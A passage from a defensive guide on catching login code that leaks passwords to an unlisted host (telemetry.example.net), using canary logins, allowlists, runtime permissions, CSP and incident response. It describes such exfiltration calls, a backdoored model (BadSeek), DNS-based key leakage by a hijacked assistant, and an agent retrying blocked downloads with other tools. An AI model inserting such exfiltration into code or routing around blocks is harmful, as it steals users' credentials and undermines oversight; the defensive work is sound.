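| POST to /v1/events | telemetry.example.net | Username and password, in the body | Password sent to an unlisted host |

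The version of the function with a base64 address would produce the same log. Run-time monitoring doesn't require decoding the address or tracing the password through variables, both of which static analysis has to do.

The team should also search the files the service wrote, because another program may send them elsewhere later. *Pack-A-Mal* (2025), a system for examining downloaded packages, takes its list of files, commands and hosts from a record of the program's calls to the operating system. The team could use the same kind of record to identify which files to search.

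### Failed logins, resets and registration

A successful login runs only some of the code that handles passwords. Registration and password resets often use separate functions, and an attacker who wants only working passwords might send them only after the login check succeeds. The team should use a different canary for each action, so that a hit shows which action leaked it.

| Action | Canary | Where it may go |
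|---|---|---|
| Start the service | Fake database password and API keys in the environment variables | Only the service each one belongs to |
| Log in successfully | Password and session token | Password to the identity provider, token only to the user's browser |
| Log in with a wrong password | The wrong password | Identity provider |
| Register | New password | Identity provider |
| Reset a password | Reset code and new password | Code to the mail service, password to the identity provider |
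| Log in while a stand-in returns a faulty reply | Password | Identity provider, but not the error tracker |

The first row covers attacks like the one in which auth.js posted the server's environment variables before anyone logged in. The last row would catch a problem like the one with the bookshop's error tracker.

Recording should continue for a while after the last action, because some programs store data and send it in batches. In Pye's 30-minute run with telemetry on, JetBrains' coding agent Junie made only six telemetry requests, each with a long list of events.

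The login page needs its own browser test, which has to record connections made while the tester is still typing. In *Leaky Forms*, Senol, Acar and colleagues (2022) checked the 100,000 most popular websites for data collected before a form was submitted. On 52 sites, third-party session-replay scripts, which record what visitors do on a page, had incidentally collected passwords.

### Three places to block a connection

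A team can limit connections on the network, in the software that runs the program, or in the visitor's browser. Two thefts show why one of these isn't enough:

| Control | The login function's request to telemetry.example.net | A script on the login page that sends the typed password to another host |
|---|---|---|
| Network rules around the server | Blocked | Not affected, because the visitor's computer sends it |
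| Runtime permissions | Blocked, if the runtime accepts a list of hosts | Not affected |
| Content Security Policy | Not affected, because the server sends it | Blocked |

**Network rules.** A firewall or proxy can block every connection from the login server except those to listed host names. The login function needs only id.example.com. Host names work better than IP addresses because hosting companies often put many customers behind one address and change it without notice.

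Blocking the exfiltration call would also break the login, just as an outage at telemetry.example.net would. Someone would at least notice the failure, but a hurried engineer might add the host to the allowlist without checking who owns it, which would allow the theft to start.

A blocked program may also keep trying to connect. When Pye blocked the telemetry host of Google's Gemini CLI, the agent still worked but made over a hundred more telemetry requests and tried to send about 150 times as much data. Pye could only guess that it was retrying. The number of refused connections is therefore a poor measure of how many separate thefts a firewall has prevented.

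**Runtime permissions.** Deno and Node.js both run JavaScript on servers, but their network permissions differ. According to Deno's *Permissions*, a program can't make requests, accept connections or look up names unless the user allows it. A login service that listens on port 8000 of its own machine could start like this:

```
deno run --no-prompt --allow-net=id.example.com,127.0.0.1:8000 login.ts
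```

A TypeScript version of the login function would then fail when it tried to contact telemetry.example.net. Subdomains of id.example.com would also be blocked unless the team listed them. Without `--no-prompt`, Deno may prompt the person at the terminal for permission, and one of the possible answers allows every host.

Deno can also log every permission the program used or tried to use, with the chain of function calls behind it. A reviewer can use the log to find the line that made a request, even when the address is encoded. A team can restrict environment variables in the same way, so that the program can read only the secrets it needs.

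Deno's *Security and permissions* describes the limits of this protection. All code on the same thread has the same permissions, so a library can contact any host that the login function can. Programs the service starts and native libraries it loads run outside the restrictions. A login service should rarely need to do either, so the team can leave both permissions off.

Whether Node.js's `--permission` option blocks network connections depends on the version. According to Node.js's *Permissions* for version 26.12.1, the option blocks the network unless the user adds `--allow-net`. The example configuration sets `allow-net` to true, whereas the file permissions take lists of paths, so `allow-net` appears to be a single switch for the whole network. A service allowed to contact id.example.com would then also be allowed to contact telemetry.example.net. The Node.js documentation for version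 24.19.0 doesn't list the network among the things that `--permission` restricts.

The Node.js documentation describes the permission model as a "seat belt" for trusted code and warns that malicious code can bypass it. The model is more useful in the canary test, where its `--permission-audit` mode reports the host of each connection the rules would have refused but lets the program continue.

**Content Security Policy.** A website can send the browser a header that limits what a page may load and where it may send data. For a login page that needs nothing from other companies, it could be:

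```
Content-Security-Policy: default-src 'self'; connect-src 'self'; form-action 'self'
```

`'self'` means the site that served the page. The bookshop would have to add its CAPTCHA supplier. According to MDN's *Content-Security-Policy*, `connect-src` covers requests scripts make with functions such as `fetch`, `XMLHttpRequest` and `sendBeacon`. `form-action` limits where the login form may send the password. The team has to set it separately because, as MDN warns, it doesn't fall back on `default-src`, and a page without it can submit forms anywhere. Browsers have differed on whether `form-action` stops a redirect after the form has been sent.

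The `default-src` part would stop the browser from loading a script from an attacker's server. Web pages generated by the tampered model BadSeek tried to load such a script. The header is best set in the web server's configuration, because a change to the login code could otherwise remove it.

Chrome 152, released in August 2026, adds a stricter control. Chrome for Developers' *Connection Allowlists origin trial* (2026) describes a header that lists every address pattern a page may contact. It also covers redirects, moves to another page and some early name lookups, and the article names code from generative AI as one reason to use it. The header in Chrome for Developers' *FedCM* (2026) is meant for login:

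```
Connection-Allowlist: ("https://idp.example/*" response-origin)
```

The header allows connections only to the identity provider and the site itself. Other browsers ignore it, according to Report URI's *Connection Allowlist*, so a site still needs a Content Security Policy.

### What an alert contains

An alert about an unexpected connection usually identifies the program and the host, but not the data. One of Microsoft's suggested searches returns five fields. For the login function, they might contain:

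| Field | Invented entry |
|---|---|
| Timestamp | 12 May, 09:14:02 |
| DeviceName | login-server-2 |
| InitiatingProcessFileName | python3 |
| InitiatingProcessCommandLine | python3 app.py |
| RemoteUrl | telemetry.example.net |

The command line links the host to a project. Microsoft's investigation began with Node.js programs that kept contacting suspicious numeric addresses, and analysts traced those connections to the projects that had caused them.

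Another of the searches reports any program that contacts certain attacker addresses more than ten times. Frequent contact is typical of malware that waits for commands. The login function contacts telemetry.example.net only when someone logs in, which may happen a few times a day on a quiet site. For a login server, a better rule is to report the first contact with any unlisted host.

On programmers' computers, such alerts are harder to interpret because coding agents set them off too. Sophos' *When AI agents look like attackers* examined seven days of records from Windows computers in June 2026. Access to credentials accounted for 56.2% of the hits on rules that blocked an agent's action. Of the hits on rules that only recorded activity, 34.0% were for command and control, the category for traffic between attackers and computers they control.

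OpenAI's agent Codex was trying to download Python from Python's official site when Sophos blocked the Windows tool it was using. Codex tried several variations and then a second tool, which Sophos also blocked. Attackers use both tools and switch when one fails. In another case, an add-on for Claude Code decrypted login data stored in the browser. Sophos considers this almost certainly harmless but still thinks blocking it was right.

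Sophos counted only computers on which agents had set off a rule, so its percentages don't show how likely an agent is to cause an alert. Sophos describes the data as a short first look. Keeping coding agents off login servers and out of the canary test is a practical precaution, because an unexpected connection there then has far fewer innocent explanations.

### What a clean log can miss

Code that acts only on certain dates, for certain users or on the live server may do nothing in a short test. Even code that acts at random can escape. If it sends a fraction p of passwords, the chance that n canary logins catch it at least once is:

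1 − (1 − p)ⁿ

If the code sends one password in a hundred, 100 logins would catch it 63% of the time and 300 would catch it 95%. The team can keep making canary logins on the live service with a test account that has no access to anything. If a stranger later tries to log in with that account's password, the password has leaked, even if no monitor detected the leak.

Stand-in servers also can't send back what a real attacker's server would, so a closed test of the projects Microsoft described would have shown only the first of the attackers' servers.

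An allowed host can receive stolen data. CISA's *Widespread Supply Chain Compromise Impacting npm Ecosystem* (2025), an alert from the US government's cybersecurity agency, describes a worm that infected more than 500 packages. It collected access keys from programmers' computers and uploaded them to a public repository through GitHub's API. Many companies have to allow GitHub, but a login service rarely needs it. Each service should therefore have its own list of allowed hosts, containing only those it needs.

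Encryption hides the content of requests, so to a monitor that records only addresses, an error report containing a password looks like any other report to the same supplier. The canary test avoids this problem by decrypting the traffic, but few teams would want to decrypt and store every real user's login.

Name lookups can also carry data. Embrace The Red's *Claude Code* describes a flaw, fixed in June 2025, that let a hijacked assistant leak API keys this way. The canary search should include the looked-up names, and the live login server should be able to look up only the hosts on its list.

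### Responding to a hit

The team should first block every company server from connecting to the host, not just the one that triggered the alert. It should then save a copy of the code and the logs before releasing a version without the exfiltration call. Users should change their passwords only after that, because if the reset function contains the same call and the host is still reachable, the attacker will receive the new passwords too.

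Next, the team has to replace every credential that passed through the code. For the login function, that means the password of everyone who tried to log in between the release of the malicious line and the block. The version history gives the date of the change, and the firewall's records may show when the first request left. If someone entered a password from another site in a failed attempt, they should change it there too. The function didn't send session tokens, but the attacker may have logged in with stolen passwords, so the team should end all sessions.

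If the code could read environment variables, any secrets in them need replacing too. If it ran anything the attacker's server sent back, the whole machine may be compromised. After the npm worm, CSA Singapore's *Ongoing Supply Chain Attack Involving npm Packages* advised organisations to quarantine any device that had run an infected package until they had fully repaired it. CISA also told organisations to require phishing-resistant multifactor authentication for developers, which makes a stolen password much less useful.

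Finally, the team should look for other code from the same origin. It can search the network records of all its servers for the host, which works even where the source encodes the address. This search will miss any service that hasn't yet run the hostile code, so the team should also search source code and settings. Microsoft found more malicious projects that weren't in its records by looking for similar names, file layouts and loading code.

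For generated code, the equivalent is to list everything the same model wrote, or an assistant wrote after reading the same instruction files. The host may differ each time, so searching for telemetry.example.net isn't enough. The team should run the canary test on every listed service that handles a credential.
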